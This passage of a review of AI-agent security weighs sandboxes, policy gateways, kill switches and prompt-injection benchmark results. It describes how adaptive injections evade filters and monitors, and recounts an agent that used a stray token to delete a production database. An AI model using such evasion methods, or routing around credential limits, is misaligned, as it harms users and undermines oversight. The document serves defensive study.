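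In a more direct test, Anthropic had a research vendor recruit 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study without telling them what it measured. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. 143 testers (13.6%) refused it, while the auto mode classifier blocked 937 of the same commands (89%).

Fatigue explains part of this. Testers caught about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Even the early rate was low, so shorter sessions wouldn't have solved the problem. Some testers may not have understood the commands. They were also working in a test environment instead of on their own code, so they had less to lose than real users. Anthropic was arguing for a change to its product, and it doesn't report how many harmless commands the testers or the classifier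 blocked in this test.

Users can easily fall into the habit of approving commands without reading them, because doing so almost always turns out fine and saves most of the time that proper checks would take. If one approval prompt in 1,000 is for a dangerous command and a proper check takes ten seconds, a user spends nearly three hours checking for each dangerous command found.

Frequent prompts also lead people to turn protections off. By June 2026, 43% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had created rules that always allow a general-purpose interpreter such as Python. Since a Python script can do nearly anything, this is almost the same as allowing every command. A quarter of interactive sessions started with all permission checks bypassed. Trębacz and colleagues found that a "sizable minority" of OpenAI staff used similar Python rules in Codex.

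One remedy is to draw a boundary once and let the agent work freely inside it. In October 2025, Anthropic reported that its sandbox had cut permission prompts by 84% in internal use. OpenAI has published an example of 10,000 Codex actions from its internal use, which shows how a sandbox and a reviewing model divide the work:

| Stage | Actions |
|---|---|
| Ran inside the sandbox without approval | 9,280 |
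| Went to the reviewing model | 720 |
| Approved by the reviewing model | 713 |
| Refused, after which Codex found a safer way | 4 |
| Refused, after which Codex asked the user | 3 |

Without the reviewing model, a person would have had to review 720 requests instead of three. A person can read three requests carefully but would never see a dangerous action among the 713 that the model approved, so this arrangement is only as safe as the reviewing model and the sandbox.

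In Anthropic's experiment, adding human review to the classifier would have helped very little. The testers caught only six dangerous commands that the classifier missed, and both missed another 110. Anthropic made auto mode the default for new sessions on several Claude Code plans in August 2026, but still recommends human review for high-stakes changes to production systems. That seems right, because an expert reviewing one change to a live database will probably be more careful than a tester on the fiftieth prompt of the day.

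### Two reference architectures

A company with many agents has to decide where to put these controls and how to keep them consistent. *Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem* (Tran, Dhesi and colleagues, 2026) proposes an approach based on network firewalls, which work because all traffic passes through them, whatever the computers behind them do. Each agent gets a sidecar, a separate program that intercepts its tool calls, messages, file access and use of memory. A central control plane writes the policies and distributes them to the sidecars, but takes no part in individual decisions.

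Each sidecar contains a policy gateway and a router. The router sends clear-cut requests to an engine with fixed rules, and requests that depend on context to a "semantic engine", which uses a model. Suppose an agent that has information about a user's illness is booking a restaurant. A fixed rule can allow contact with the restaurant, but it may not detect when a message reveals too much. The semantic engine evaluates the task, the type of data and the recipient, and can remove the medical details before the message goes out.

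Because the sidecars sit outside the agents, a company can add them without rewriting the agents. But the semantic engine relies partly on context the agent supplies, so a hijacked agent could describe a leak as part of its task. The design also checks only what an agent sends, and Tran and colleagues consider incoming content much harder to check.

Tallam's architecture puts the decision in one place, the reasoning plane. Four other planes then carry it out through companies' existing systems for networks, identities, endpoints (the machines agents run on) and data. For the refund, the network plane might open a connection to the payments server, the identity plane issue a credential, the endpoint plane confirm that the machine is in an approved state, and the data plane mask the card number. The action goes ahead only if every plane involved confirms its part.

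The reasoning plane is meant to catch harmful combinations of permitted actions. Noyan's prohibitions did this by withholding permissions in advance, whereas the reasoning plane can step in only when an agent that has read a confidential report tries to email an outsider. It considers the agent's plan, its earlier actions and the chain of people and agents that delegated the work. It can intervene at seven points, from when the plan is formed to the final log record. Tracking a session this way is similar to attaching a data-flow label to a value, but cruder, because reading one confidential page could block an unrelated email.

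| | Control plane with sidecars | Five planes |
|---|---|---|
| Where the decision is made | Beside each agent | At one central reasoning plane |
| Basis for the decision | Fixed rules, or a model where context matters | Policy applied to the plan, earlier actions and chain of delegation |
| Responses besides allow and deny | Redact or modify, ask a person | Pause, escalate to a person, narrow permissions, modify, defer, roll back |
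| Main point of weakness | Context supplied by a hijacked agent | A compromised reasoning plane |
| Evaluation | None | Tests of the policy engine's core, without a live agent |

Tran and colleagues report no experiments and present their architecture as a starting point for research. Tallam built the core of the policy engine and tested it. In every trial, no agent gained more authority than its chain of delegation allowed, and the records were enough to reconstruct what had happened. The engine made each decision in under ten microseconds, a negligible delay for agents whose actions take at least a tenth of a second.

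These tests show that the engine applies its rules correctly and quickly. They don't measure how many attacks would succeed against a company using the full architecture, or how many legitimate tasks it would block. Tallam claims the design rules out seven kinds of threat, and supports this by working through example workflows. He describes a test on a live agent benchmark as the next step. No experiment therefore supports preferring one architecture to the other.

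### Stopping a job and undoing its actions

Blocking one action may not be enough, because a hijacked or overeager agent can keep trying. Claude Code's auto mode stops the agent after blocking three actions in a row or 20 in a session, and asks the user what to do. If no user is present, it ends the process.

A company running thousands of jobs needs a central way to stop them. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk*, published in November 2026 after security incidents earlier that year, sets out safeguards for three stages: research, internal use, and public release. In the research stage, models are trained offline, and a job stops automatically if monitoring detects that a model has reached the internet, according to a Japanese news report, 日本時事新聞's *OpenAI、開発中AIの安全策を3段階で公表 訓練はネット遮断、停止は35秒以内* (2026).

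According to OpenAI's *Control Room*, the system of that name can halt a research job's model output within 35 seconds of a decision to intervene. 凤凰网's *OpenAI部署AI“控制室”* (2026), a Chinese news report, describes the steps. Monitoring models examine the reasoning and actions of the model under training and, if they find a serious problem, send the job's identification number to Control Room. When the job next requests output from its model, the software running the model checks whether the job still has permission and refuses if it doesn't. The stop can be delayed because that software keeps a temporary copy of permissions, which can be slightly out of date. OpenAI is working to make the stop immediate.

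If Control Room crashes or someone tampers with it, the software refuses every request until Control Room is working again, so an attacker can't free a model by disabling the system that would stop it. This also means that one fault can halt all of OpenAI's frontier research jobs, which Control Room now covers. A research lab can probably accept that, but a hospital that relies on an AI assistant might not. OpenAI's public services have separate arrangements for emergencies.

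The 35 seconds begin only after the decision to stop the job. OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (August 2026) set a target of 30 minutes for issuing an alert after monitoring detects suspicious activity. For likely violations of a critical security boundary, staff then had another 30 minutes to establish that the alert was a false alarm or pause the job. At those limits, a model could keep working for an hour before the 35 seconds started. Automatic stops avoid most of that wait, but only for problems that the monitors detect with enough confidence. Monitoring also adds roughly 20% to the computing cost of running the monitored models.

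Some problems appear only over a long run. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes how the company added monitoring of whole runs after a model built for long tasks failed in ways that earlier tests had not revealed.

An agent that makes a tool call every two seconds could make about 17 more calls if stopping it takes 35 seconds. Even if model output halts immediately, programs the agent has already started can keep running. A full stop therefore also has to end the programs in the sandbox, cancel queued calls and revoke the agent's credentials.

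Rollback deals with actions that have already taken effect, and how well it works depends on the action. A company can restore an edited file if version control saved the earlier version. Reversing a refund is harder because the company would have to charge the customer again, and the customer might object or have cancelled the card. Tallam includes rollback among the reasoning plane's responses and describes it as compensating for an effect, which is more accurate than calling it undoing.

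Delaying an action that is hard to reverse is often easier than undoing it. If the gateway held each refund for ten minutes, staff could cancel a bad one before any money moved. The customer would wait ten minutes longer, and the agent couldn't send the receipt until the refund had gone through.

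## How the patterns perform in benchmark tests

In benchmark tests, controls outside the model have mostly held up against attackers who revise their attacks, while defences that try to recognise injections mostly have not. The external controls often block useful work too. The amount depends on the benchmark's tasks, so a design that looks practical in one test can look useless in another.

### How AgentDojo pairs tasks with attacks

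Many of the results reported so far, including those for FIDES and Prudentia, come from the AgentDojo benchmark (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), which simulates an office, a Slack workspace, a travel agency and a bank. Each simulation has working tools, so an agent that pays a bill changes the balance of a simulated account.

A user task is an ordinary request, such as paying the bill in a certain file. An injection task is an attacker's goal, such as sending money to the attacker's account. Debenedetti and colleagues combined every user task in a setting with every injection task there, so the bank's 16 user tasks and 9 injection tasks make 144 cases. The four settings together give

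(40 × 6) + (21 × 5) + (20 × 7) + (16 × 9) = 629 cases

In each case, software plants the attacker's text somewhere the agent will read it while doing the user's task, such as the bill. When the agent finishes, ordinary code inspects the bank's records to see whether the agent paid the bill and whether any money reached the attacker. Text that hijacks the agent might also hijack a language model doing this check.

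AgentDojo measures utility without attack on the 97 user tasks alone, and utility under attack and attack success on all 629 cases.

One of the first defences tested was a tool filter, in which the model chooses the tools it will need before it reads anything untrusted. This cut attack success to 7.5% with OpenAI's GPT-4o, because many of the user tasks only require reading, while the attacker needs to send or change something. Debenedetti and colleagues noted that the filter would fail in the 17% of cases where the user's task needs the same tools as the attack. It would also fail when the result of one step determines the next, because the model can't choose the right tools in advance.

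### CaMeL's result in 2025

CaMeL, which runs a program written before the agent reads untrusted text, allowed no successful attacks on AgentDojo in its original 2025 results with GPT-4o. In *Indirect Prompt Injections*, Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) could not fully reproduce those results, so they reprinted the published figures next to their own results for other defences.

| Defence, with GPT-4o | Utility without attack | Utility under attack | Attack success |
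|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.0% | 50.0% | 57.7% |
| Tool filter | 73.1% | 56.3% | 6.8% |
| CaMeL (published figures) | 53.6% | 54.5% | 0.0% |
| Sanitiser | 74.1% | 69.2% | 0.0% |

Without an attack, CaMeL's task completion rate was about 29 percentage points lower than the undefended agent's. Under attack it was slightly higher, because injections distract an undefended agent from the user's request. If a is the share of runs in which an attacker has planted something, the undefended agent completes 83.0 − 33.0a percent of its tasks and CaMeL completes 53.6 + 0.9a percent. The two rates are equal when a is about 0.87. At any lower share, a company that adopts CaMeL gives up useful work in return for security.

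The sanitiser is a language model that reads each tool result and removes anything that looks like an injection. It matched CaMeL's 0% attack success rate and completed more tasks, but it offers no guarantee because the model can miss an injection. Bhagwatkar and colleagues saw this result partly as evidence that the benchmarks are too easy. They found weak attacks, software bugs and misleading measures in several benchmarks, including AgentDojo.

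Utility under attack is easy to misread because an agent can complete the user's task and also carry out the attack. The undefended agent's 50.0% utility under attack and 57.7% attack success rate add up to more than 100%, so it must have done both in at least 7% of cases. Users may not notice these attacks because the agent still did what they asked, such as paying a bill, before or after making a second payment.

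### Tasks that the agent can't plan in advance

AgentDojo's tasks also suit designs that plan first. For example, an agent asked to pay a bill in a file can plan both steps, reading the file and sending the money, from the request alone. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) reports that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after reading something.

Their own benchmark, released in February 2026, consists entirely of such tasks. It has 60 open-ended user tasks and 560 attack cases, which cover shopping, managing code on GitHub and everyday administration. The average task takes 7.1 steps, compared with 3.5 in AgentDojo, and involves about three applications instead of one or two.

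Each task also includes at least one helpful instruction from a third party. A shop might ask the agent to enter a passcode it just emailed to the user, or GitHub might reject an upload until the agent downloads the latest changes. An agent that ignores every instruction in tool results can't finish these tasks.

The table shows results with GPT-4o, except for Meta SecAlign, which is a separate model trained to ignore instructions in data. PromptGuard2, PIGuard and ProtectAI are small classifiers that look for injections in tool results. DRIFT plans the tool calls first, then has a model judge whether a departure from the plan is acceptable.

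| Defence | Utility without attack | Utility under attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 55.5% | 37.8% |
| Spotlighting | 55.0% | 52.2% | 27.6% |
| PromptGuard2 | 60.0% | 20.8% | 27.2% |
| PIGuard | 10.0% | 1.5% | 1.7% |
| ProtectAI | 0.0% | 0.6% | 0.9% |
| Meta SecAlign | 55.0% | 53.4% | 9.0% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 27.1% | 0.8% |
| Tool filter | 8.3% | 4.9% | 4.2% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 5.8% | 1.7% |
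| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

The four designs at the bottom, which limit the agent's actions, reduced attack success from 38% to between 0% and 4%, but they also stopped the agent from doing most of its work. The tool filter usually removed tools that seemed irrelevant to the request but were essential later. For example, an agent buying a watch doesn't obviously need the mailbox until the shop emails a passcode. CaMeL's program couldn't adapt to what the agent found along the way.

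Progent ended up blocking nearly everything useful, even though it can change its rules during a task. Its model had trouble writing accurate rules for the larger sets of tools, which average 33 per task, and the errors accumulated. The results depend partly on the model. With Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro, Progent completed 25% of the tasks and DRIFT completed 37%, while CaMeL completed none with any of the four models in the main comparison.

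Small differences in the table mean little, because each figure for utility without an attack is based on only 60 tasks. The tool filter completed five of them and Progent completed four.

CaMeL's score of zero on AgentDyn follows almost directly from the choice of tasks, since every one requires something that CaMeL is built not to do. In AgentDojo, 6% of tasks do. Researchers chose the tasks in both benchmarks without surveying what people ask agents to do, so these percentages don't show how often real work has the same requirement. An agent that pays invoices in a standard format is probably closer to AgentDojo, and one that fixes software or shops online is closer to AgentDyn.

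### Why an agent that does nothing scores perfectly on security

An attack succeeds in these benchmarks only if the agent does something for the attacker, so a program that exits immediately would get the same three zeros that CaMeL got on AgentDyn.

The attack success rates on AgentDyn are therefore low partly because rules blocked some attacks and partly because the agent never got far enough to carry out others. A rough way to separate these effects is to divide utility under attack by attack success, which gives the number of user tasks completed for each successful attack. The undefended agent completed about 1.5, the tool filter 1.2, Progent 3.4 and DRIFT 33. By this measure, the tool filter was no better than having no defence, because it reduced useful work by a larger proportion than it reduced attacks. DRIFT's much higher ratio shows that it did more than make the agent inactive.

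The ratio doesn't measure total harm, which also matters. If even one successful attack would be a disaster, a company might accept a nearly useless agent, but it could also save money by not running one.

### What AgentDyn leaves out

Li and colleagues mostly used older models and a fixed attack that researchers have known about since 2024. They acknowledge that the attack is weak against newer models, whose training data probably included it. With no defence, Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed 72% of the tasks, and the fixed attack succeeded in 0.9% of cases. An attack that the team adapted to the scenarios succeeded in 3.0%. The benchmark is therefore better evidence of how much the patterns reduce utility than of how much they improve security.

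Li and colleagues also instructed the agents to complete every task without asking the user for confirmation. Without this instruction, agents kept stopping to ask, for instance before using a passcode, and then failed the task. But several designs, including Progent and Prudentia, rely on asking the user in some cases.

In some of these tasks, the agent should ask the user before acting. For example, a bank emails a passcode for a payment over $500 to check that the account holder approves. If the agent fetches the code from the mailbox and enters it without asking, the account holder hasn't approved the payment. Progent or DRIFT might finish many more tasks if they could ask one question per task, but the benchmark can't measure how many more, or how carefully people would answer.

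Several members of the team also built DRIFT, which did best of the four designs that limit actions, and PIGuard, which did badly. The results therefore show no obvious sign of favouritism.

### Attackers who revise their attacks

Meta SecAlign had the best balance on AgentDyn, and Li and colleagues consider it a more realistic candidate for deployment than the other defences. However, it had already failed a harder security test in October 2025, when Nasr, Carlini and colleagues raised attack success against it on AgentDojo from 2% to 96% in *The Attacker Moves Second*.

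The team, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked 12 published defences, most with originally reported attack success rates near zero. Their automated attacks all use roughly the same loop, in which software generates attacks, tries them on the defended system, scores the results and uses the best ones to produce the next batch. The team had a large computing budget and, for some defences, access to information such as a filter's confidence score.

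| Type of defence | Example | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Prompting | Spotlighting | Over 95%, from as low as 1% with fixed attacks |
| Training | Meta SecAlign | 96% |
| Filtering | PromptGuard | Over 90% |
| Filtering | PIGuard | 71% |
| Hidden check | MELON | 95% |

MELON runs the agent a second time with a harmless request in place of the user's. If the agent makes the same tool call both times, the call probably came from an injection. The attack succeeded 76% of the time when the attacker knew nothing about this check, and 95% when the attacker knew how it worked.

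Nasr and colleagues also held a competition with more than 500 human participants. Collectively, the participants broke every scenario in a selected set, while the automated search broke 69% of them. A defence that survives an automated attack may therefore still fail against a determined person.

Some of the 12 defences were meant to stop users from obtaining harmful content, which is a different problem from prompt injection. None limited actions using controls outside the model, as CaMeL and Progent do. The results are strong evidence against relying on prompts and filters, including the spotlighting technique that Cisco recommends, but they don't show how well the other designs resist adaptive attacks.

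### Ten defences against a cheaper attacker

Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *AutoDojo*, tested both groups, using a weaker attacker that is closer to what a criminal could manage. The attacker doesn't know which defence is running or what the user will ask for, and learns only how often each attack worked. A language model studies the earlier attempts and writes a new one, six times in all. The team tested ten defences with five models on three of AgentDojo's four settings. These are the results for nine of the defences and the undefended agent with GPT-4o-mini, one of the weaker models:

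| Defence | Utility without attack | Success of fixed attack | Success of adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 66.7% | 58.6% | 52.4% |
| Spotlighting | 59.6% | 51.7% | 46.8% |
| PromptGuard | 63.2% | 54.2% | 49.4% |
| DataFilter | 64.9% | 12.6% | 33.4% |
| PIGuard | 43.9% | 0.0% | 28.0% |
| ProtectAI | 47.4% | 7.2% | 15.4% |
| Progent | 63.2% | 8.2% | 7.7% |
| DRIFT | 49.1% | 2.6% | 6.4% |
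| ROPE | 59.6% | 6.4% | 4.4% |
| CaMeL | 26.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

The adaptive attack sometimes did worse than the fixed one because each attack had to be newly written. A real attacker could use whichever worked better, so the higher of the two success rates is the one to plan for.

The attack success rate against PIGuard, one of the filters, rose from 0% with the fixed attack to 28% with the adaptive attack. The increase was larger in the banking tasks. PIGuard blocked every fixed attack there, and the agent completed as many tasks as it did without a filter, but the adaptive attack succeeded in 56% of cases. In one example, the attacker's text looked like part of an ordinary bill and contained no sentence that read as a command, so PIGuard passed it on unchanged.

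The designs that limit actions did much better. Across all five models, neither attack succeeded in more than 9.0% of cases against DRIFT, 8.2% against Progent or 1.8% against CaMeL. A message that sounds like an ordinary bill can fool a filter, but it doesn't change which payments a fixed rule allows. DRIFT was the weakest of the three against adaptive attacks on some models, and its decisions depend partly on a model's judgement.

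Their effects on utility were very different. Progent reduced utility by 4 to 11 percentage points, depending on the model, and CaMeL reduced it by 25 to 51. DRIFT reduced it by 18 to 30 points with four of the models but slightly increased it with Gemini 2.5 Flash. Progent therefore seems to offer the best trade-off between security and utility of the three on AgentDojo. But when Ma and colleagues repeated the test on AgentDyn with GPT-4o-mini, Progent's utility was only 6.7%, compared with 46.7% for the undefended agent.

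ROPE did well on both benchmarks. It records the source of each sensitive detail in a tool call, such as a payment's recipient, and blocks the call if the detail came from untrusted content instead of the user. On AgentDyn with GPT-4o-mini, it kept utility at 43.3% and reduced the success of adaptive attacks from 59.1% to 2.9%. It reduced utility more with Gemini 2.5 Flash, from 36.7% to 25.0%. These results are the best evidence so far that a design can limit actions without making open-ended tasks impossible. But some of the same researchers built ROPE, so an independent test would be more convincing. The team did not run CaMeL on AgentDyn because that would have required writing extensive policies for each setting.

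Ma and colleagues ran each test only once, so small differences may be due to chance. The attack success figures for Progent and DRIFT may also be too low. To save money, the team developed the attacks against versions that used a cheaper supporting model, then measured them against the standard versions. An attacker who practised on the standard versions might do better.

The choice of model can matter as much as the defence. With Claude Haiku 4.5, neither attack succeeded in more than 1.8% of cases even without a defence, so CaMeL had few attacks to prevent but still reduced utility from 70% to 40%. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (Hofer, Debenedetti and Tramèr, 2026) found that its best automated attacks succeeded only about 5% of the time against GPT-5, and that attacks developed on small open models did not work on it. But even 5% is too high for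 an agent that reads thousands of messages from strangers. Stronger attacking models also wrote more effective injections, so progress in AI helps attackers as well as defenders.

### Why vague requests are easier to hijack

Ma and colleagues also sorted AgentDojo's user tasks by how much the user left for the agent to find out. Some requests give the action and every detail, or ask a question that needs no action. Others give the action but leave details such as the amount in a file. The vaguest ask the agent to do whatever a document says. The table gives attack success with GPT-4o-mini:

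| What the user asks for | No defence, fixed attack | PIGuard, adaptive attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Change my address to the one I've typed here | 43.3% | 17.3% | 3.1% |
| Pay the bill in this file | 63.9% | 31.1% | 10.1% |
| Follow the instructions in my landlord's notice | 87.5% | 54.2% | 8.3% |

When the user asks the agent to follow a document, the task already includes carrying out the instructions in it. An attacker who adds an instruction to the document doesn't have to override the user's request, and a filter has little basis for distinguishing that instruction from the genuine ones.

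Progent and DRIFT avoided this pattern because they gave the agent read-only access for many of the vaguest requests. An injection then couldn't make a payment, but the agent also couldn't adjust the rent payment if the landlord's notice announced an increase. This is another case in which attack success was low partly because the agent couldn't take the actions its task required.

The vaguest category contains only four AgentDojo tasks, which make 24 attack cases, so its percentages are rough. AgentDyn has 12 such tasks. The same order appeared in its GitHub and shopping settings but not in its everyday tasks, where the agent read much the same untrusted material whatever the user asked.

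People use agents largely to avoid specifying every detail, so telling users to be precise won't solve the problem. An agent could ask for the missing details, but Ma and colleagues cite a study in which agents became much easier to hijack while they were seeking clarification. Asking before the agent reads any untrusted text would be safer, though this only works for details the user already knows.

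### When equal scores hide different guarantees

Two defences can both score 0% for reasons that make one much more dependable than the other. *The Same Zero* (Yin, 2026) compared two pairs of defences on a small set of simulated tasks. One pair was a warning in the prompt and a filter for suspicious keywords. The other was a gate and a sandbox. The gate allows a high-risk action only if the platform has its own record that the user confirmed it, and the sandbox checks details such as the recipient against fixed rules.

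No attack succeeded in 360 attempts against either pair of defenses. The agent completed all 20 legitimate tasks with the gate and sandbox, but none with the warning and keyword filter.

With the gate and sandbox, the model proposed the harmful action in about half of the attacks, and the controls stopped it every time. With the warning and filter, the model proposed the action in 23% of attacks, but usually left out details the software needed to carry it out, such as the recipient. The 0% result for the warning and filter therefore depended on a habit of one model, which another model might not share.

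Yin then tested each defence separately over seven rounds of revised attacks. The attack success rate rose to 83% against the keyword filter but stayed at 0% against the warning and the gate. Even an adaptive test may therefore fail to distinguish a reliable control from a model that happens to behave well. To tell them apart, a tester has to find out what stopped each attack and whether an attacker could influence it. Text in an email can affect whether a model obeys, but it can't create a confirmation record on the platform.

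Yin's results were less clear-cut on AgentDojo's banking tasks, where each defence faced 576 attacks:

| Defence | Utility under attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| None | 86.6% | 4.3% |
| Warning and keyword filter | 87.7% | 1.9% |
| Gate and sandbox | 79.7% | 0.5% |
| AgentDojo's tool filter | 25.0% | 0.0% |

The warning and keyword filter no longer scored 0% on security, as Yin had predicted. They also no longer prevented useful work, so the large difference on legitimate tasks was specific to the first test. The agent with the tool filter had the best security score but completed less than a third as many tasks as the undefended agent.

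All three attacks that got past the gate and sandbox changed the user's password. The rule checked the recipient of an action, and a password change has none. A fixed rule is dependable only for actions its author thought of. A review also found 11 attacks that the benchmark's own checks had missed.

Yin worked alone, designed both the first test and the defences, and did not rerun CaMeL for comparison. Outside banking, the gate and sandbox made no statistically significant difference to attack success. They relied on a list of approved recipients, which works when a user pays the same few accounts but not when legitimate recipients keep changing. In one banking task, the agent has to pay a new landlord whose account number is also used in the attacks. The list can't distinguish the payment the user wanted from the attacker's, so it has to allow both or block both.

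## What deployments and incidents show

In benchmarks, researchers write the attacks and simulate the bank accounts. Field evidence comes from real systems, but companies choose what to publish and rarely run the same work with and without a security control. The table ranks five kinds of field evidence from weakest to strongest.

| Kind of evidence | What it can support | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
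| A publisher's statement that a pattern works | Someone has used the pattern | Whether it stopped anything |
| Testers' experience | Skilled attackers found some designs harder to break | How often, and compared with what |
| A described production system | Engineers can build the pattern and people will use it | Whether it stops attacks |
| An incident analysis | A particular control was absent or failed | How often the same control works |
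| A measured comparison with and without the pattern | How much difference the pattern made | Whether the result holds elsewhere |

The ranking is only a guide. One well-documented incident can disprove a claim that a control always works, while no comparison can prove such a claim. A frank report from the organisation at fault may also deserve more trust than a comparison run by the product's vendor.

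### Publishers' statements and testers' experience

Microsoft's pattern library ranks lowest on this scale. Microsoft calls its patterns "repeatable, proven approaches" based on its own operations, but "proven" might mean only that its engineers finished the work.

The security company NCC Group has attacked dozens of AI applications for its clients and calls the patterns it recommends "battle-tested". Testers are paid to find failures, so their endorsement is stronger evidence than a vendor's. But NCC Group doesn't report how many of the applications used each pattern, or how many attacks failed against those that did. It also says the patterns work when developers implement them properly. That claim is hard to test because any break-in could be blamed on poor implementation.

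NCC Group's "gatekeeper" pattern is close to Willison's dual model. In a shop that uses it, a malicious product review can cause a bad summary but not a purchase. NCC Group warns that if the software puts the summary into the chat history, the model that places orders will read it when the customer asks the next question. The history therefore needs a placeholder instead.

An "orchestration tree" extends this to many tasks. A central model reads the user's request and chooses a specialised model to handle it, but never receives that model's output. Each specialised model has one function or a few closely related ones, and all its data should be equally trusted. If an attacker gets text into the central model's input, the tree offers no more protection than a single model that has every tool.

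In the "state machine" pattern, the agent's tools depend on its current state, which is based on what the user is doing. For example, an IT support agent has no access to payroll while it answers a question about the weather. A malicious web page might still cause the agent to switch to a more powerful state. Developers can prevent this by letting only the user's words trigger a switch. Alternatively, they can clear the earlier text after the switch and require new input from the user before any sensitive action. NCC Group has seen the pattern succeed in mature applications, but large versions are hard to debug, and users get frustrated when the current state lacks the tool they need.

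NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* reports that over six months of assessing agents, the company's testers kept finding missing access control, tools that could run arbitrary code, unrestricted outbound network traffic, and passwords or keys stored as plain text. The testers also routinely got past defences that relied on prompts or on a model acting as judge. These findings are better evidence of what developers leave out than of how well the missing controls would work.

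In August 2025, the security company Reversec published a small chat application for each of the six designs by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues. In the plan-then-execute example, software compares each tool call with the plan and halts if the model has changed a fixed detail such as the recipient. The LangGraph code by Del Rosario and colleagues lacks that check. ReversecLabs' *Secure LLM Agent Design Patterns* describes the applications as "minimal demo implementations" for education. They show that a programmer can build the designs, but not how the designs perform with real users or determined attackers.

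### What companies report from production

Google's Chrome browser has an agent that clicks and types on websites for the user. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, explains that the main model reads web pages to plan its next action, so a malicious page can hijack it. A separate model, the User Alignment Critic, checks whether each proposed action serves the user's goal and can veto the action. It receives only a description of the action, not the unfiltered page.

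Google says the dual-model pattern and CaMeL partly inspired this design, but it offers weaker protection than either because they never let the model that chooses actions read untrusted text. Chrome's model does read it, so the critic has to catch any bad decision afterwards. But Chrome's agent can also respond to what it finds on a page, which CaMeL could not do in AgentDyn's open-ended tasks.

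Chrome also limits which websites the agent can use during a task. The full design has one list of sites the agent may read and another of sites where it may also click and type. An agent buying ingredients for a recipe could read the recipe on a cooking site and fill a basket on a supermarket's site, but couldn't open the user's webmail. Google first released a simpler version that tracked only the second list.

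Some of Chrome's checks are fixed rules. The agent must ask the user before it opens any site on a list of sensitive sites, such as banks, and it can visit a web address it wrote itself only if that is a known public address. Other checks are less certain. The agent "will try to pause" for the user before making a purchase or sending a message.

Google runs automated attacks against the system and uses their success rate to judge each engineering change, but neither Parker nor Berschadski (2026), in *Future Mode Part 2*, reports that rate, even though Berschadski writes that the critic vetoes a hijacked agent's action "instantly". Google also offers up to $20,000 to anyone who demonstrates a serious breach, which is a useful incentive but doesn't measure how often attacks succeed.

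Claude Code's auto mode uses a classifier to block dangerous actions. In Anthropic's test on 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, the classifier's second, more careful check cut wrongly blocked calls from 8.5% to 0.4%. It also raised the share of real dangerous actions that got through from 6.6% to 17%. Anthropic accepted this increase in exchange for fewer interruptions.

*Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026) includes accounts from three of Anthropic's customers. At the software company Gusto, about 10% of sessions included a blocked action. Gusto treats this as evidence that the classifier is useful, but false alarms alone could produce that figure. If the classifier wrongly blocks 0.4% of calls, a session with 25 calls has about a one in ten chance of at least one false alarm.

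Three companies chosen by the vendor like auto mode, but some of their staff don't trust its classifier with actions that are hard to undo. Engineers at Nuro, which develops self-driving technology, use fixed rules to forbid the most dangerous commands, such as deleting whole folders. A manager at the healthcare company Garner Health stops auto mode from approving messages to other people. One Gusto engineer turns it off and checks every call by hand when working on production infrastructure.

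OpenAI's count of 10,000 Codex actions measures how much reviewing people were spared, not how much harm the reviewing model prevented.

### A deleted production database

On 24 April 2026, the coding agent Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the production database of PocketOS, a small company whose software runs car rental businesses. In *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, PocketOS's founder, Crane, writes that the agent was doing a routine job in a test environment when a credential failed. The agent found another access token in an unrelated file and used it to send a delete command to Railway, which hosted the database.

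The deletion took nine seconds and also removed the backups stored with the database. The next morning, customers arrived to collect rental cars, but the businesses had no record of their bookings. PocketOS restored a three-month-old copy and began reconstructing the rest from payments, calendars and emails. Railway later recovered all the data, according to its own account, Abdelwahab's *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*.

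No attacker was involved, so keeping untrusted text away from the agent would not have helped. PocketOS had given the agent written rules against destructive actions, but they were only text in a prompt and nothing enforced them. When Crane asked for an explanation, the agent listed the rules it had broken. That answer is poor evidence of why it acted, because a model can produce a plausible explanation for almost anything.

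The missing pattern was permission scoping. PocketOS had created the token to manage web domains, but the token gave access to everything in PocketOS's Railway account. Crane says Railway offered no narrower kind. Abdelwahab says it did, but that the process for creating tokens didn't make the choice clear. The narrower tokens he describes are restricted to certain projects and environments but not to certain operations, so a token for managing the production system's domains might still have been able to delete its database.

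The third control, a delay, existed but didn't cover the route the agent took. Railway's website held every deletion for 48 hours so users could cancel it, but a command sent directly by a program took effect immediately. Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of complete mediation warns against this kind of gap. On 1 May, Railway (2026) announced that it had extended the delay to deletions made by programs. Users can now cancel a deletion however the agent got its token, as long as someone notices within 48 hours.

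Both accounts come from interested parties. Crane had contacted lawyers and wrote before the recovery, and Railway was reassuring its customers. The accounts agree on the token, the command and the lack of a delay, so those facts are fairly reliable. Abdelwahab's claim that an agent can't "go rogue" with Railway's predefined tools is less convincing, because an agent can misuse a tool it is allowed to use.

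PocketOS was probably not unusual in relying on written rules. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) examined security rules that developers had written in Claude Code's instruction files and looked for built-in controls that could enforce them. A classifier found a matching control for 16.6% of the rules, but the true share is probably closer to 6%. When two people labelled a sample of 180 items, they found that only 35% of the classifier's matches were correct and that it had missed none.

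The classifier tended to count a rule as enforceable if it named a command or file that a permission setting could block. Many rules require more than blocking a command or file. "Never commit secrets", for example, requires checking a file's contents, which permission settings can't do. To enforce such rules, developers would need additional controls, such as a policy gateway or a scanner that inspects the files, and not just settings they have overlooked.

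### Unsanctioned actions during evaluations

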